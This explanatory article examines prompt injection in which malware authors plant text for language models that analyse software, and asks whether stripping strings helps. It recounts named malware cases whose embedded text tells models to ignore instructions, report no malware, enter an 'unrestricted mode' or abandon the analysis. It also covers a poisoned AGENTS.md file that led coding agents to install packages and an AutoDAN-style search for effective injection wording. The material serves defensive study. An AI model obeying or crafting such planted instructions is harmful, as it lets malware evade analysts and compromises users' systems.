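# Prompt injection through text in analysed software, and whether stripping strings prevents it

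## How does text inside a program reach a language model?

Prompt injection is an attack in which someone other than a language model's operator writes text that ends up in the model's input and changes what the model does or concludes. It can work wherever a system passes outside material to a model, such as a web page, an email, a job application or a computer program. Security teams now use language models to judge whether programs are malicious, work out what they do and look for flaws in them, and a program's author can include sentences meant for the model. Security companies have already found malware that contains such sentences. One proposed defence is string stripping, which removes or masks readable text before the program reaches the model.

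Text inside a program reaches a language model through an analysis pipeline, which is the set of tools and prompts that turn the program into text, give that text to the model and use the model's answer. How much stripping strings can achieve depends on this pipeline.

### One sequence of tokens

A language model works on tokens, which are words, parts of words or symbols. It produces an answer one token at a time, each time estimating which token is likely to come next. Crawford, Phillips and McClure (2026), in *Automatically Attacking Software Reverse Engineering AI Agents*, write the quantity that the model computes as

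$$P(r_{m+1} \mid q_1 \dots q_n, r_1 \dots r_m)$$

where the *q*'s are the tokens of the input and the *r*'s are the tokens of the answer so far. The model picks a token according to these probabilities, adds it to the answer and repeats the calculation until it produces a marker that ends its turn. The operator's instructions, the analyst's question and the text of the suspicious program are all among the *q*'s. Nothing in the expression records who wrote which.

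Developers use a chat template to mark whether each part of the input comes from the system's operator, the user or a tool. The markers are tokens in the same sequence as the text, and *The Self-Correction Illusion* (2026) documents that they differ between model families. Training gives the model a tendency to treat text differently depending on the marker around it. However, *LLMON* (2026), which proposes a markup language for model input, points out that a transformer (the type of network behind these models) does not automatically enforce a line between instructions and data.

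Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026), in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*, measured how much role markers affect the way a model represents text. They wrapped identical passages of web text in five different role markers and trained a simple classifier to tell, from the model's internal activations, which marker surrounded a passage. Because the wording was identical, the classifier could learn only the effect of the marker. They then applied it to a short conversation about gardening, using the open-weight model gpt-oss-20b. The model's reasoning passages scored 85% as "reasoning" under the correct markers, 83% with no markers, and 85% when the whole conversation was wrapped in markers for user text, so the style of the writing had more effect than the markers. One conversation is a small test, but Ye and colleagues report similar results for other roles and other models. Labelling a program's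 text as tool output therefore gives the model some information about where the text came from, but does not guarantee that the model will act on it.

Databases can separate commands from data more reliably than language models can. In SQL injection, an attacker types text into a web form and a database runs it as a command. Programmers can prevent this with parameterised queries, which keep the user's data apart from the command so that the database never runs the data. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a December 2025 post from the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, David C argues that language models have no such separation and that prompt injection may never have a comparable complete fix.

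### Direct and indirect prompt injection

The US standards institute, NIST (2025), calls prompt injection direct when the attacker is the system's primary user and enters the text personally. It is indirect when the attacker changes an outside resource, such as a document or web page, that the model later takes in. The term "prompt injection" dates from 2022, and *Not what you've signed up for* (2023) described indirect attacks on applications built around language models, including search, a year later.

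Text planted in a program is indirect prompt injection, since the program's author has no access to the analyst's session. The case is borderline when the analyst copies code from the program and pastes it into a chat window. The software security organisation OWASP defines direct injection by the channel through which the text arrives, and its *LLM01:2025 Prompt Injection* includes text that a user enters inadvertently, so pasted code could count as direct. Under NIST's definition it remains indirect, because the user is not the attacker. NIST's definition suits software analysis better, because the program's author wrote the text whether a tool or a person moved it into the prompt.

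### Three uses of language models on software

The first use is classifying a program as malicious or benign. Chawla and Prasad (2026), in *A Decompilation-Driven Framework for Malware Detection with Large Language Models*, built a pipeline that converts Windows programs into C code and gives the code to a model, along with other static analysis of the file (information obtained without running it). They prompt the model to act as an expert in malware analysis, look for suspicious functions and patterns, and answer only "True" for malware or "False". Google's Gemini 2.5 Pro, since superseded, labelled 71 of 120 malicious files from 2025 as malicious (59%). After fine-tuning on 200 example files, it labelled 101 as malicious (84%). A one-word answer is convenient for automation, but it leaves the model no room to report anything odd in the text.

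The conversion to C is necessary because ordinary language models cannot interpret a program's raw bytes, but it makes the input much larger. One 187 KB file in Chawla and Prasad's collection became about 2.5 MB of text, and they had to leave out many samples that exceeded the models' input limits. *Large Byte Model* (Störtz, Servia-Rodríguez and colleagues, 2026) describes an exception, a model from the security company CrowdStrike with 5,120 additional tokens that represent sequences of bytes. It identified a file's processor architecture with up to 98% accuracy and its malware family with 69%. CrowdStrike has given the model to a limited number of analysts, and most pipelines still convert programs to text.

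Reverse engineering, which means working out what a compiled program does without its source code, is a more open-ended use. A disassembler translates the machine code into assembly language, and a decompiler goes further and reconstructs approximate source code, usually in C. Cisco Talos, the security research group of the network company Cisco, connected two models to the disassembler IDA Pro and had them analyse a known malware sample of about 37 functions. The researchers asked for a report on the program from its entry point onwards, an explanation of one particular function, and descriptive names for all the unnamed functions. Claude 3.7 Sonnet used 328 tool operations to name the functions, at a cost of 13.24 dollars. The researchers didn't tell the models that the file was malicious, because in earlier attempts a phrase in the prompt saying so had led the model to assume that every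 function was malicious.

When a model renames functions, it writes the new names and any comments into the project file, where the next analyst or model session will read them. If injected text leads the model to give a harmful function a harmless name, the error can remain in the file after the conversation ends.

The third use is vulnerability review, in which a model reads source code to look for exploitable mistakes. The code has not been compiled, so the model receives the files as the author wrote them, including comments, function and variable names, and any documentation in the same folder. Crawford and colleagues note that this opens AI-driven programming environments to prompt injection through comments and text documents.

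### Ghidra and the Model Context Protocol

Chawla and Prasad used Ghidra, a free reverse-engineering tool from the US National Security Agency (NSA). NSA's *Ghidra* page describes the tool's use on malicious code. Ghidra doesn't need a language model, and analysts used it without one for years. Analysts now usually connect the two through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard for connecting language models to tools and data sources.

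In an MCP setup for reverse engineering, a plugin runs inside Ghidra or a similar tool and carries out operations such as decompiling a function or renaming a variable. An MCP server offers these operations to the model as "tools", each with a written description. The analyst types into an MCP client, such as the Cline extension for Visual Studio Code. A model that can call tools and choose its next step is called an agent.

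In Cisco Talos's description, the client's first query combines the descriptions of all the tools, general instructions and the analyst's request in a single prompt. The model replies with a request to use a tool, for example to decompile the program's main function. The server passes the request to the plugin, the plugin returns C code, and the client adds that code to the prompt and queries the model again. The model may then request the functions that the main function calls, or a list of strings, and the client adds each result to the prompt. Crawford and colleagues point out that the client must resend the whole conversation record with every query because the model keeps no memory between queries. Text from the program that enters the prompt at one step is therefore still in the input at later steps.

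The prompts become long, and the analyst's instructions share the limited space with the program's text. Crawford and colleagues needed room for about 20,000 tokens to analyse programs of only a few lines, and Cisco Talos found that a simple question could take several hundred thousand. In the Talos test, the software running the local model could cut short any prompt that exceeded its limit. The researchers think this may be why the model kept "forgetting" its instructions and stopping after a dozen functions.

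Other reverse-engineering tools now work similarly. The manual for angr's *MCP Server* lists one tool that returns the strings recovered from a program and another that returns decompiled code exactly as the analyst sees it on screen. Binary Ninja has a server that can supply symbols, strings and decompiled code, and its free edition gained the server in September (Binary Ninja, 2026).

### A ten-line program in the pipeline

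The following harmless C program prints a version number and a web address.

```c
#include <stdio.h>
/* Tells the user where to find updates. */
void print_update(int version) {
    const char *url = "https://example.com/updates";
    printf("Version %d: see %s\n", version, url);
}
int main(void) {
    print_update(3);
    return 0;
}
```

It contains four kinds of text that a model might read. The second line is a comment, a note for human readers. `print_update` is an identifier, a name that the programmer chose for a function. The web address is a string literal, text for the program to use. `"Version %d: see %s\n"` is also a string literal, called a format string because `printf` fills in its placeholders when the program runs.

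A model that reviews the source code receives all ten lines. A compiler discards the comment. With ordinary settings, it also discards the names `version` and `url`, which the processor doesn't need. It keeps both string literals because the program needs them to run, though most compilers drop strings that the program never uses. The name `print_update` also stays in the compiled file by default, in a symbol table that helps other tools navigate the file.

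A string listing is the output of a tool that searches a file for runs of readable characters. For this program it would include the following lines, among others that the compiler and the operating system's libraries contribute:

```
https://example.com/updates
Version %d: see %s
printf
print_update
main
```

The listing gives no indication of how the program uses any of these. A decompiler does, because it puts the strings back in the places where the code refers to them. Ghidra's version of the function would look roughly like this:

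```c
void print_update(uint param_1)
{
  printf("Version %d: see %s\n", param_1, "https://example.com/updates");
  return;
}
```

The variable `version` has become `param_1`, a name that Ghidra made up, and `url` has disappeared.

Many malware and commercial software developers delete the symbol table before they release a program, which produces a "stripped binary". In this example, the function would lose its name and Ghidra would substitute `FUN_` followed by an address, but both string literals would remain.

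| Text in the source file | In the string listing | In the decompiler output | In a stripped binary |
|---|---|---|---|
| Comment | No | No | No |
| `print_update` | Yes | Yes | No |
| `version` and `url` | No | No | No |
| Format string | Yes | Yes | Yes |
| Web address | Yes | Yes | Yes |

String stripping is different from stripping a binary, despite the similar name. The defender applies it to the text about to go to the model, targeting the last two rows of the table. A stripped binary can therefore contain as much injected text as any other program, and a program may still have its function names after a defender masks its strings.

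Suppose an analyst asks an agent whether this program connects to the internet. The prompt starts with the tool descriptions and the analyst's question. The agent requests the program's strings, and the client adds the listing, which includes the web address, to the prompt. The agent then requests `print_update`, and the client adds the decompiled function, which also contains the address. The correct answer is no, because the program only prints the address. An agent that relied on the listing could easily get this wrong, and seeing the address twice might make it more confident. If the program's author had replaced the address with a sentence intended for the model, that sentence would have appeared in both the listing and the function.

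### What the attacker controls

*When Binaries Talk Back* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) sets out a threat model, a statement of what an attacker can and cannot do, for reverse engineering with language models. The attacker controls the program and, through it, much of what the tools report, including strings, symbols, decompiled code and log contents. The attacker does not control the analyst's instructions, the operator's policies, the tools themselves or the model provider.

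On these assumptions, Ghidra works correctly throughout the attack, so checking it for errors or tampering would find nothing wrong. Santos-Grueiro distinguishes the origin of a record from the origin of its contents. A trustworthy tool may have created the record and accurately copied a string into it, even though the attacker wrote the string.

Santos-Grueiro also considers injected text that gives false evidence instead of instructions, such as a phrase suggesting that a program steals passwords when it has no code to do so. A string extractor, a decompiler and a summary of the analysis may each display the phrase, so a model may count one piece of text as three findings. He argues that text alone should support only an observation, and that a claim about what a program does needs evidence from its structure or behaviour. The web address in the ten-line program is an innocent example of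 the same problem.

The attacker must keep the program working and use text that survives compilation, so comments can carry an attack only in source code. Ghidra's decompiler cuts off strings after 2,048 characters, and Crawford and colleagues found that their attack failed when its text exceeded that limit. They add that a human analyst would easily recognise a long, pointless string as suspicious. However, a pipeline that returns only "True" or "False" may have no human looking at the code.

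## What have attackers written for models to read?

Malware authors have put text in their programs for language models to read. Some authors describe the program as harmless. Others tell the model to report that it found no malware, try to provoke a refusal, imitate error messages from the analysis system, or add so much filler that the code may not fit in the model's input. Most of the evidence comes from security companies that found the text while examining a file. They can report what the author wrote and reasonably guess why, but they rarely know which analysis systems received the file or what results those systems gave.

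### False descriptions

FRUITSHELL is a short script in PowerShell, a Windows scripting language. It opens a reverse shell, a connection from the victim's computer that lets the attacker run commands there. The author disguised the code by naming its variables after fruit, and put a two-line comment at the top for language models. The comment tells them that they don't need to analyse the file, and describes the script as a harmless generator of prime numbers from 1 to 1,000. No code in the script generates prime numbers, as Fetterman (2026) points out in *Ignore all instructions and read this blog*, an analysis for Cisco Talos. The comment doesn't affect the reverse shell, because PowerShell ignores comments.

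A model could accept the comment's description and still be carrying out the analyst's request, but with false information. It could also find the contradiction by reading the code below the comment, though the fruit names probably make this harder because they remove one clue to what the code does.

Fetterman calls FRUITSHELL the first malware of its kind, and the earliest sample he studied dates from January 2025. Google later reported that attackers were using it. TechCentral.ie's *AI-based malware makes attacks stealthier and more adaptive* (November 2025) covered Google's findings and listed FRUITSHELL among five families with "AI-powered capabilities", although an attacker can write a comment without AI.

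Other attackers copied the text. In the 15 months after someone first uploaded FRUITSHELL to VirusTotal, a service that scans suspicious files with many antivirus products, Talos found the same comment word for word in nine more scripts from at least four actors. None of the nine is a variant of FRUITSHELL, so these attackers copied only the comment. The scripts range from simple ones to an advanced collection that Talos calls ROZESHELL.

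Talos also traced one evasion text to a named red-team instructor, who teaches security staff to imitate attackers. According to Help Net Security's *Researchers uncover malware that uses AI to choose its next move* (2026), the text appeared in unrelated malware within 12 months of its first confirmed use in a real attack. The article doesn't identify the text, but the pattern resembles that of FRUITSHELL's comment.

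The copying is weak evidence that the comment works. Two lines of comment are easy to add and can't break a script, so an author might include them just in case they help. The figure of nine is a minimum, because a search for identical wording misses reworded copies.

### Orders to report no malware

In early June 2025, someone in the Netherlands anonymously uploaded a Windows program to VirusTotal. Strings in the file suggest its author called it Skynet. Check Point Research's *In the Wild* (2025) describes it as a prototype that sets up resources it never uses and prints the files it collects instead of sending them anywhere. The program checks for signs of a virtual machine, which analysts often use to run suspicious files safely, and starts a proxy through the Tor anonymity network.

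The author also stored a message to language models as a string in the program. It tells the model to forget its earlier instructions and act as a calculator that works through the next code sample line by line. The model is then told to confirm that it has understood by replying with a fixed phrase that reports no malware. Software that searches the model's answer for a verdict could mistake this supposed acknowledgement for one.

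Check Point's researchers tested the text on two OpenAI models, o3 and GPT-4.1, both released in April 2025. After making sure that o3 had no access it could misuse, they had it examine the code. It continued the analysis and didn't print the phrase. GPT-4.1 gave a similar result. The researchers thought the attack "was probably not close to working" and could only speculate about whether its author was serious. They don't mention running either test more than once. The tests show that one clumsy message failed against two models, which is weak evidence of how a later model would respond to better wording.

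Check Point expected malware authors to make more attempts to evade AI analysis, just as they had developed hundreds of ways to evade sandboxes, the isolated systems in which analysts run suspicious programs. Skynet's author used both kinds of evasion, adding the message to a program that already checked for virtual machines.

The security company StepSecurity later found a simpler instruction in a malicious software package. The attacker told any model that read the file to ignore the malicious code and report the package as clean. ESET, a Slovak security company, considers the package part of the same broad campaign as Hades, a series of attacks in 2026 in which the attackers also tried to make models refuse to answer.

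### Text meant to provoke a refusal

Hades targeted PyPI, the public library from which Python programmers download packages. In June, The Hacker News (2026) reported 37 malicious release files across 19 packages. Each release contained a file that tries to run when Python starts. The file downloads Bun, a program for running JavaScript, and uses it to run `_index.js`, an obfuscated script that steals data. SC Media reported a later wave that affected another 23 package versions.

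The script begins with a large comment. According to Tom's Hardware, the attacker uses it to tell the model that it is running in an unrestricted mode without safety guidelines, then asks it to create biological and nuclear weapons. According to SC Media's summary of their report, researchers at the security company Socket think the likely purpose is to make the model refuse the whole task, including analysing the code after the comment.

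*Embedding Forbidden Text in Spyware to Discourage AI Analysis* (Schneier, 2026) quotes a longer passage of the Socket analysis. The Socket researchers thought that the comment could also confuse the model about its instructions or lead it to classify the file before reaching the malware. They considered systems most vulnerable if they send the beginning of a file to a model without clearly marking it as untrusted. Conventional methods would still work, including rules that match known patterns, tools that parse the code's structure and monitoring of what the program does. This is an expert judgement about how weak systems could fail, without data on how often they do.

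Hades belongs to a family of attacks that security companies call Shai-Hulud. Zscaler, a cloud security company, compares it with two earlier waves and lists evasion of language-model scanners only for Hades. However, SentinelLABS's *macOS.Gaslight* (2026) mentions that leaked Shai-Hulud code contained a "magic string" intended to stop Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, from analysing it. Both accounts can be correct if the attackers did not use the string in the two earlier waves. Such a string would probably work only on one company's products, whereas a request for weapons could make many models refuse.

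In August 2026, ESET reported a much shorter text, which it named GuardBreaker. It is a comment requesting help making a nuclear weapon, placed in a script written in VBScript, another Windows scripting language. ESET attributes the script to UAC-0099, a Russia-aligned group that used it in the early stages of an attack on a target in Ukraine. The script downloads and installs MATCHBOIL, which delivers further malware and is used only by this group. According to Help Net Security's *Russian hackers plant nuclear weapon prompt in malware to trip AI safety* (2026), the group usually targets the transport and energy sectors and has passed targets to Sandworm, a hacking group linked to Russian military intelligence.

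ESET takes the comment as a sign that UAC-0099 expected the target's defences to use AI. In other recent attacks, the group checked whether the computer was running established analysis tools, such as the disassembler IDA. ESET doesn't report that any scanner stopped at the comment.

ESET describes the aim as making a scanner stop before it reaches the malicious code. This could happen if the pipeline sends the script in parts and gives up at the first refusal, because the model would never receive the rest. If the pipeline sends the entire script at once, the malicious code is already in the input when the model refuses, and the analyst receives no analysis of it.

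### What happens after a refusal

A refusal lets malware through only if the pipeline treats a missing answer as a pass, which a programmer could build in by accident. Chawla and Prasad's pipeline, for example, asks the model to answer "True" for malware and "False" for anything else. If a programmer gave such a pipeline a rule that blocks a file only when the answer is "True", a refusal would let the file through because it is neither word. If the rule instead allowed a file only when the answer was "False", the same refusal would block it.

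A pipeline can also send unanswered files to a person or another tool. The attacker then gains at most some time, but that can be valuable. Cisco Talos' *Sorry, I can’t help with that* (2026), a newsletter about safety restrictions on commercial models, warns that refusals can slow or halt an investigation while an attacker finishes the attack. ESET suggests that attackers could also steer an agent towards actions that require human approval and exploit the delay. An attacker could also put forbidden requests in many harmless files, leaving analysts a long queue of refusals to work through.

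Asking the model again may not help. The comment can trigger another refusal as long as it remains in the input, and an agent's client resends the whole conversation with each query.

Models may also refuse without an attacker's involvement, because safety restrictions can block material used in malware analysis. When Talos evaluated 66 combinations of language models and reasoning settings for security work, higher reasoning settings sometimes produced blocked responses. If models refuse to analyse many ordinary files, a busy security team has a reason to let unanalysed files pass, which is what an attacker who triggers a refusal needs. ESET recommends further checks whenever a model gives no answer.

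### Imitated system messages

macOS.Gaslight is malware for Apple computers that steals data and gives an attacker remote control. Someone uploaded it to VirusTotal on 22 May 2026. SentinelLABS, the research group of the security company SentinelOne, examined it after Apple added it to the malware protection built into macOS. The researchers have high confidence that it belongs to a cluster of North Korean activity. They base this on Apple's detection names for the program and a related sample, which they associate with earlier North Korean malware.

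The program contains 38 false system messages, about 3.5 KB of text in total. Some report expired tokens, processes that ended for lack of memory, a full disk or repeated failures. Others warn of injection vulnerabilities or imitate static analysis alerts. The author surrounded the messages with formatting and markers like those an analysis pipeline uses to separate its instructions from a sample's contents, so a model might treat the messages as coming from the pipeline. In Ye and colleagues' experiment, the style of a passage had more effect than its role markers, which suggests that the imitation could work even when the pipeline correctly labels the text as tool output.

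SentinelLABS thinks the author wanted an agent to abort the analysis, cut it short or refuse it. The messages can encourage this without containing an order to stop or a claim about the program. If the disk were full and every operation had failed, giving up would be sensible. Agents are probably the main target because they choose their next step. A pipeline that sends a model one question and takes a one-word answer has no long session to abandon.

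Hades also contains fake system instructions, so the categories overlap. The fake instructions in Hades lead up to a forbidden request, while those in macOS.Gaslight describe technical failures. SentinelLABS notes that earlier cases used a single block or header of injected text, and considers the series of 38 messages new.

SentinelLABS doesn't describe testing the messages on a model. When it published its report, none of the static engines on VirusTotal detected the sample. Static engines mostly search files for known patterns, while the messages are addressed to a language model, so the lack of detections isn't evidence that the messages worked.

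### Filler text

ESET describes a package on npm, a public library of JavaScript code, whose main file repeated a stock phrase of AI assistants tens of thousands of times before the malicious script. The attacker apparently wanted to fill the model's context window, the maximum amount of text it can take in at once, and leave no room for the script.

As with refusals, the result depends on the pipeline. If it sends only the beginning of an overlong file, the model receives the filler and none of the malicious code. If it splits the file into parts, the model eventually receives everything, but the analysis costs more. Filler doesn't have to persuade the model, so even a model that always ignored instructions in a sample could miss the code. ESET adds that oddly structured files might have a similar effect if a tool truncates them or reads only part of them.

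### Instructions for coding agents

On 26 October 2026, Help Net Security's *AI coding agents fall for malicious instructions planted in the Downloads folder* reported a related attack on people who use AI to write software. The company Forever Security had found a file called AGENTS.md on a customer's computer. Developers put files with this name in a project folder to give instructions to coding agents. This one contained an order to install a malicious npm package, hidden in 13 KB of ordinary-looking engineering guidelines and aimed at OpenAI's Codex.

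Forever Security's researchers report that Codex ran the malware, or in most attempts a harmless substitute that opened a calculator, more than 90% of the time. They think the file's length and dull tone helped, because Codex refused a short request to install a package. They also wrote their own file for Claude Code that presented a harmful settings change as a company's internal gateway. Claude Code made the change about half the time, and its requests then went to a server that an attacker would control.

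These rates are far higher than Skynet's, but Codex is supposed to follow an AGENTS.md file in a folder that the user has marked as trusted, whereas a malware analysis pipeline has no reason to follow a comment in a sample. The Codex case is more relevant to vulnerability review, where an agent may open a folder of unfamiliar source code that includes such a file.

### Carriers and reported effects

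The carrier determines which kind of removal could affect the text. The five named malware cases use two carriers.

| Case | Reported | Carrier | Aim | Reported effect on a model |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| FRUITSHELL | November 2025 | Comment in a PowerShell script | Make the script seem harmless | No success reported in a real attack |
| Skynet | June 2025 | String in a compiled program | Obtain a "no malware" answer | Failed on o3 and GPT-4.1 |
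| Hades | June 2026 | Comment in a JavaScript file | Provoke a refusal | No success reported in a real attack |
| macOS.Gaslight | June 2026 | String in a compiled program | Make an agent abandon the analysis | No success reported in a real attack |
| GuardBreaker | August 2026 | Comment in a VBScript file | Provoke a refusal | No success reported in a real attack |

Removing every string but keeping comments would remove the injected text from Skynet and macOS.Gaslight but leave it in the other three. Removing only comments would do the reverse. This is because the other three are scripts, which reach the victim as source code with their comments intact, while Skynet and macOS.Gaslight are compiled programs, which do not.

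The lack of reported successes is only weak evidence that these texts fail. If one worked, the pipeline would label the file as clean or give no answer, and perhaps nobody would look at it again. People noticed the known cases by other means. In Talos's tests, the best techniques moved the result in the attacker's favour in about 35% of runs, so some injected text can work.

### Talos's count of 84 samples

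Talos counted 84 malware samples containing text intended to influence AI analysis, collected from January 2025 to July 2026. They belong to four families, which Talos calls FRUITSHELL, PLOTSAFE, HOLLOWCLAD and MANTLEMAZE. The last three names don't match those of the other cases described here, but security companies often give different names to the same malware, so the cases may overlap.

The count can't show how common the technique is, because Talos searched specifically for files that contain such text. *Introducing CAIRN* (Fetterman, 2026) describes the search tool. CAIRN searches information that other systems have already extracted from files, including strings, antivirus labels and records of what a program did in a sandbox. It doesn't download or run the malware. It has up to 24 filters for different signs of AI use, and one of them looks for text explicitly addressed to AI analysis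 systems. A search like this is a good way to find examples, but to estimate what share of malware contains injected text, researchers would need to examine a random sample.

The search could also miss many cases. A filter for text that mentions AI or addresses an analysis system might overlook GuardBreaker's comment, which does neither. CAIRN also can't find text that the extraction tools failed to recover, or files that nobody submitted for scanning.

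However, the 84 samples may represent fewer than 84 attacks or authors. An attacker who makes small changes to a program and releases it again creates another sample, and some files may be experiments, as Skynet appears to have been. A rise in the number of samples would also be hard to interpret, because attackers could be using the technique more widely or security companies could be looking for it more carefully.

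## How often does injected text change the result?

In published tests, the effect of injected text ranges from none to success on every program. The most detailed figures come from Cloudflare (2026), an internet infrastructure company that added deceptive comments to malicious scripts and gave the scripts to seven language models. Adding 20 comments made almost no difference on average, though it sharply lowered one model's detection rate. Cloudflare also reported that comments work best when they make up less than 1% of a file, but file size probably explains this more than the comments do.

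### The "Notice to AI" scripts

Cloudflare lets customers run small programs called Workers on its servers. In March 2026, its threat researchers were monitoring a surge in Workers used as VPNs and proxies. One Worker contained thousands of lines of comments, labelled as a notice to AI code reviewers and automated audit systems. The comments describe the file as part of a legitimate private project that performs routine operations and doesn't collect data without permission, and they repeat this in several languages, including Spanish, Croatian and Lithuanian. Like FRUITSHELL's comment, they give the model a false description but no instructions.

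The researchers first put similar comments at the top of short pieces of code (about 2,000 tokens). This backfired with most of the cheaper models, which became more likely to label the code malicious. A real scanner usually receives a whole script, and an attacker can scatter comments through it, so the researchers then ran a larger experiment.

The researchers took 100 scripts that Cloudflare had blocked as malicious or abusive. About half were for phishing and a third for proxies or tunnelling, while the rest hosted files or abused streaming services. They made 23 variants of each script, with up to 1,000 comments in English, Estonian, Arabic, Chinese or Russian placed at random points between statements. Although the scripts were real, their combination with the comments was artificial. Cloudflare acknowledges that comments inserted this way may be less subtle than an attacker's own.

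The company doesn't name the models, but it calls three of them "frontier" (flagship systems) and four "non-frontier" (faster and cheaper ones). The table gives the share of scripts that each model labelled malicious.

| Model | No comments | 20 comments | 1,000 comments |
|---|---|---|---|
| Frontier 1 | 67% | 67% | 76% |
| Frontier 2 | 61% | 64% | 68% |
| Frontier 3 | 62% | 67% | 75% |
| Non-frontier 1 | 90% | 67% | 72% |
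| Non-frontier 2 | 65% | 75% | 91% |
| Non-frontier 3 | 72% | 67% | 68% |
| Non-frontier 4 | 59% | 65% | 72% |

Across the seven models, the average detection rate was 68% without comments, 67% with 20 comments and 75% with 1,000. One model's fall from 90% to 67% is too large to dismiss as chance, but changes of a few points could easily be noise in a test of 100 scripts. The researchers think 1,000 comments raised detection because models treated so much repetition as a sign of fraud.

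Part of that rise might come from how Cloudflare counted malformed answers. With 1,000 or more comments, two of the frontier models sometimes returned garbled text or a refusal instead of a verdict. Cloudflare left malformed answers out of some of its figures. If it also left them out of these figures, and they came mostly from scripts that were hard to judge, the detection rate would rise even if the models were no better at recognising malware.

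For most models, the number of comments affected detection more than their language did. With 1,000 comments, the average detection rate ranged from 73% for Estonian to 78% for Russian. The largest difference was in Non-frontier 3, which labelled 68% of scripts malicious when the comments were in English and 82% when they were in Russian.

All 100 scripts were malicious or abusive, so a model that labelled every file malicious would have scored 100%, and the experiment can't measure how often the models would wrongly flag harmless code.

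### Does the share of comments matter?

The researchers also grouped the English results by how much of each file the comments took up. They give no figure for shares between 10% and 25%.

| Comments as a share of the file | Valid answers | Labelled malicious |
|---|---|---|
| None | 789 | 67.3% |
| Under 1% | 2,528 | 53.3% |
| 1–10% | 822 | 77.0% |
| 25–50% | 283 | 97.9% |
| Over 50% | 439 | 98.9% |

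Detection fell by 14 percentage points, or about a fifth, to 53.3%. Cloudflare concludes that a small share of comments can nudge a model towards a "benign" verdict, but a large share reveals the attack. It considers the share more important than the number of comments.

However, the share also depends on the size of the script. About 1 KB of comments makes up 1% of a 100 KB script, while a 3 MB script needs about 30 KB to reach the same share. As comments are added, large scripts therefore stay in the "under 1%" group through most of the increases, while small scripts soon leave it. The results by file size show that even without injected comments, the models were much worse at detecting large malicious scripts.

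| File size | Scripts | No comments | 1 comment | 20 comments |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Under 100 KB | 36 | 94.1% | 93.7% | 99.0% |
| 100–500 KB | 18 | 100.0% | 100.0% | 100.0% |
| 500 KB–1 MB | 3 | 70.8% | 65.2% | 63.6% |
| 1–3 MB | 10 | 70.0% | 69.6% | 72.5% |
| Over 3 MB | 33 | 17.6% | 13.6% | 12.3% |

A rough calculation shows that file size alone could explain the result. Without comments, the models detected 17.6% of the scripts over 3 MB and about 91% of the others. If comments had no effect on any verdict, and scripts over 3 MB supplied just over half of the answers in the "under 1%" group, detection in that group would still be 53.3%. These scripts make up a third of the whole collection and are probably more common in this group.

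The same applies to the groups with the largest share of comments, which must consist mostly of small scripts. The models detected 98–99% of the scripts in these groups, only slightly more than the 96% or so they detected among scripts under 500 KB with no comments. Across all four groups with comments, they detected 66%, about one point below the rate without comments.

The results by file size are a fairer test because they compare the same scripts with and without comments. Adding twenty comments raised detection by about 5 points in the smallest scripts and lowered it by about 5 in the largest. The 7-point fall between 500 KB and 1 MB comes from only three scripts. Among scripts over 3 MB, the fall from 17.6% to 12.3% is roughly a dozen verdicts out of about 250. Comments may have a small effect on large files, where detection is already poor, but the effect is far smaller than the 14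 points that the grouping by share suggests.

The study therefore separates the effect of the number of comments from that of file size, at least up to 20 comments, but not the effect of the comments' share of the file. That would require comparing different shares among scripts of similar size, or padding one script with harmless code to several sizes while keeping the share constant.

Cloudflare's pooled averages may include results that are missing from its table of seven models. Running seven models on 100 scripts in 23 variants would require 16,100 calls, but Cloudflare reports 18,400. It also counts 789 valid answers for the scripts without comments, when seven models could have given at most 700. Both numbers would fit eight sets of answers, but the company doesn't explain the discrepancy.

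### Why the models missed large scripts

The models' input limits ranged from 376 KB to 2.8 MB, so none could read a whole script larger than 3 MB. The researchers shortened 47 scripts to fit. If this removed the malicious part, the model could not find it.

Cloudflare reports that models also missed malicious code that did fit. In some scripts, the code that sent stolen data to the messaging service Telegram sat among thousands of lines from ordinary software libraries. The researchers think the harmless code diluted the models' attention, but they give no separate detection rates for complete and shortened scripts. They also didn't test the same script at different sizes, so the large scripts may have differed from the small ones in other ways, such as the type of abuse.

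Non-frontier 1, the model that 20 comments affected most, had the smallest limit and the highest detection rate. Only 67 scripts were 3 MB or smaller, so a rate of 90% suggests that it labelled at least 23 of the 33 largest scripts malicious after reading no more than about an eighth of each. Either that part contained enough evidence, or the model tended to call a file malicious when in doubt. If it did tend to do that, reassuring comments could have led it to label doubtful files harmless instead. Testing the model on harmless scripts would help to distinguish the two explanations.

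Models missed more than four-fifths of the largest scripts even when the researchers had added nothing to them, so deleting comments wouldn't solve the problem of file size. An attacker may gain more by bundling a large library with the malicious code than by writing any message to the model.

### Talos's test runs

In Cisco Talos's tests, the best techniques succeeded about 35% of the time, so the average across all techniques must be lower. Fetterman calls the effect inconsistent.

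The figure counts outcomes that favour the attacker, which include refusals to answer and less serious assessments as well as "benign" verdicts, so it doesn't measure a fall in detection rate. It also doesn't mean that about a third of the malware samples Talos collected evaded analysis in real attacks.

An injected message that works 35% of the time would offer little protection against a careful analyst who runs the model several times and investigates any disagreement, but it could still help an attacker who can try repeatedly. If each attempt had an independent 35% chance of success, an attacker who released five versions of a program would have an 88% chance that at least one would succeed. The real figure would probably be lower, because a message that fails in one version is likely to fail in the next.

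### An attack that searches for its own wording

The messages in known malware seem to be mostly guesswork. Crawford and colleagues, at the US Naval Postgraduate School, instead used an algorithm to find wording that worked on a particular model. They targeted an agent that used Ghidra through the Model Context Protocol, with Cline as the client, and tried to make it describe a different program from the one it was analysing.

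The researchers adapted AutoDAN, an algorithm that other researchers had designed to make models answer forbidden requests. It is a genetic algorithm, which means that it improves a set of candidates over many rounds by keeping the best and combining or slightly changing them. Here the candidates were short sentences for the injected text. The algorithm scored each by how likely it made the answer that the attacker wanted:

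$$P(t_1 \dots t_k \mid q_1 \dots q_n) = \prod_{i=1}^{k} P(t_i \mid q_1 \dots q_n, t_1 \dots t_{i-1})$$

The *q*'s are the tokens of the input, including the candidate sentences, and the *t*'s are the tokens of the desired answer. Each factor is the same next-token probability that the model computes whenever it generates text. The score can rank two candidates that both fail, so the search can build on the one that came closer to producing the desired answer. An attacker who sees only the model's final answers has much less information to guide the search.

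The algorithm had to test each candidate within the full record of the agent's conversation, so it needed a model that could take in long text. The software ran on a single graphics processor, which could handle models of about 8 billion parameters (the numbers a model learns in training). Few models that small could take in such a long conversation. The researchers chose Qwen3-8B, an open-weight model (one that anyone can download and run).

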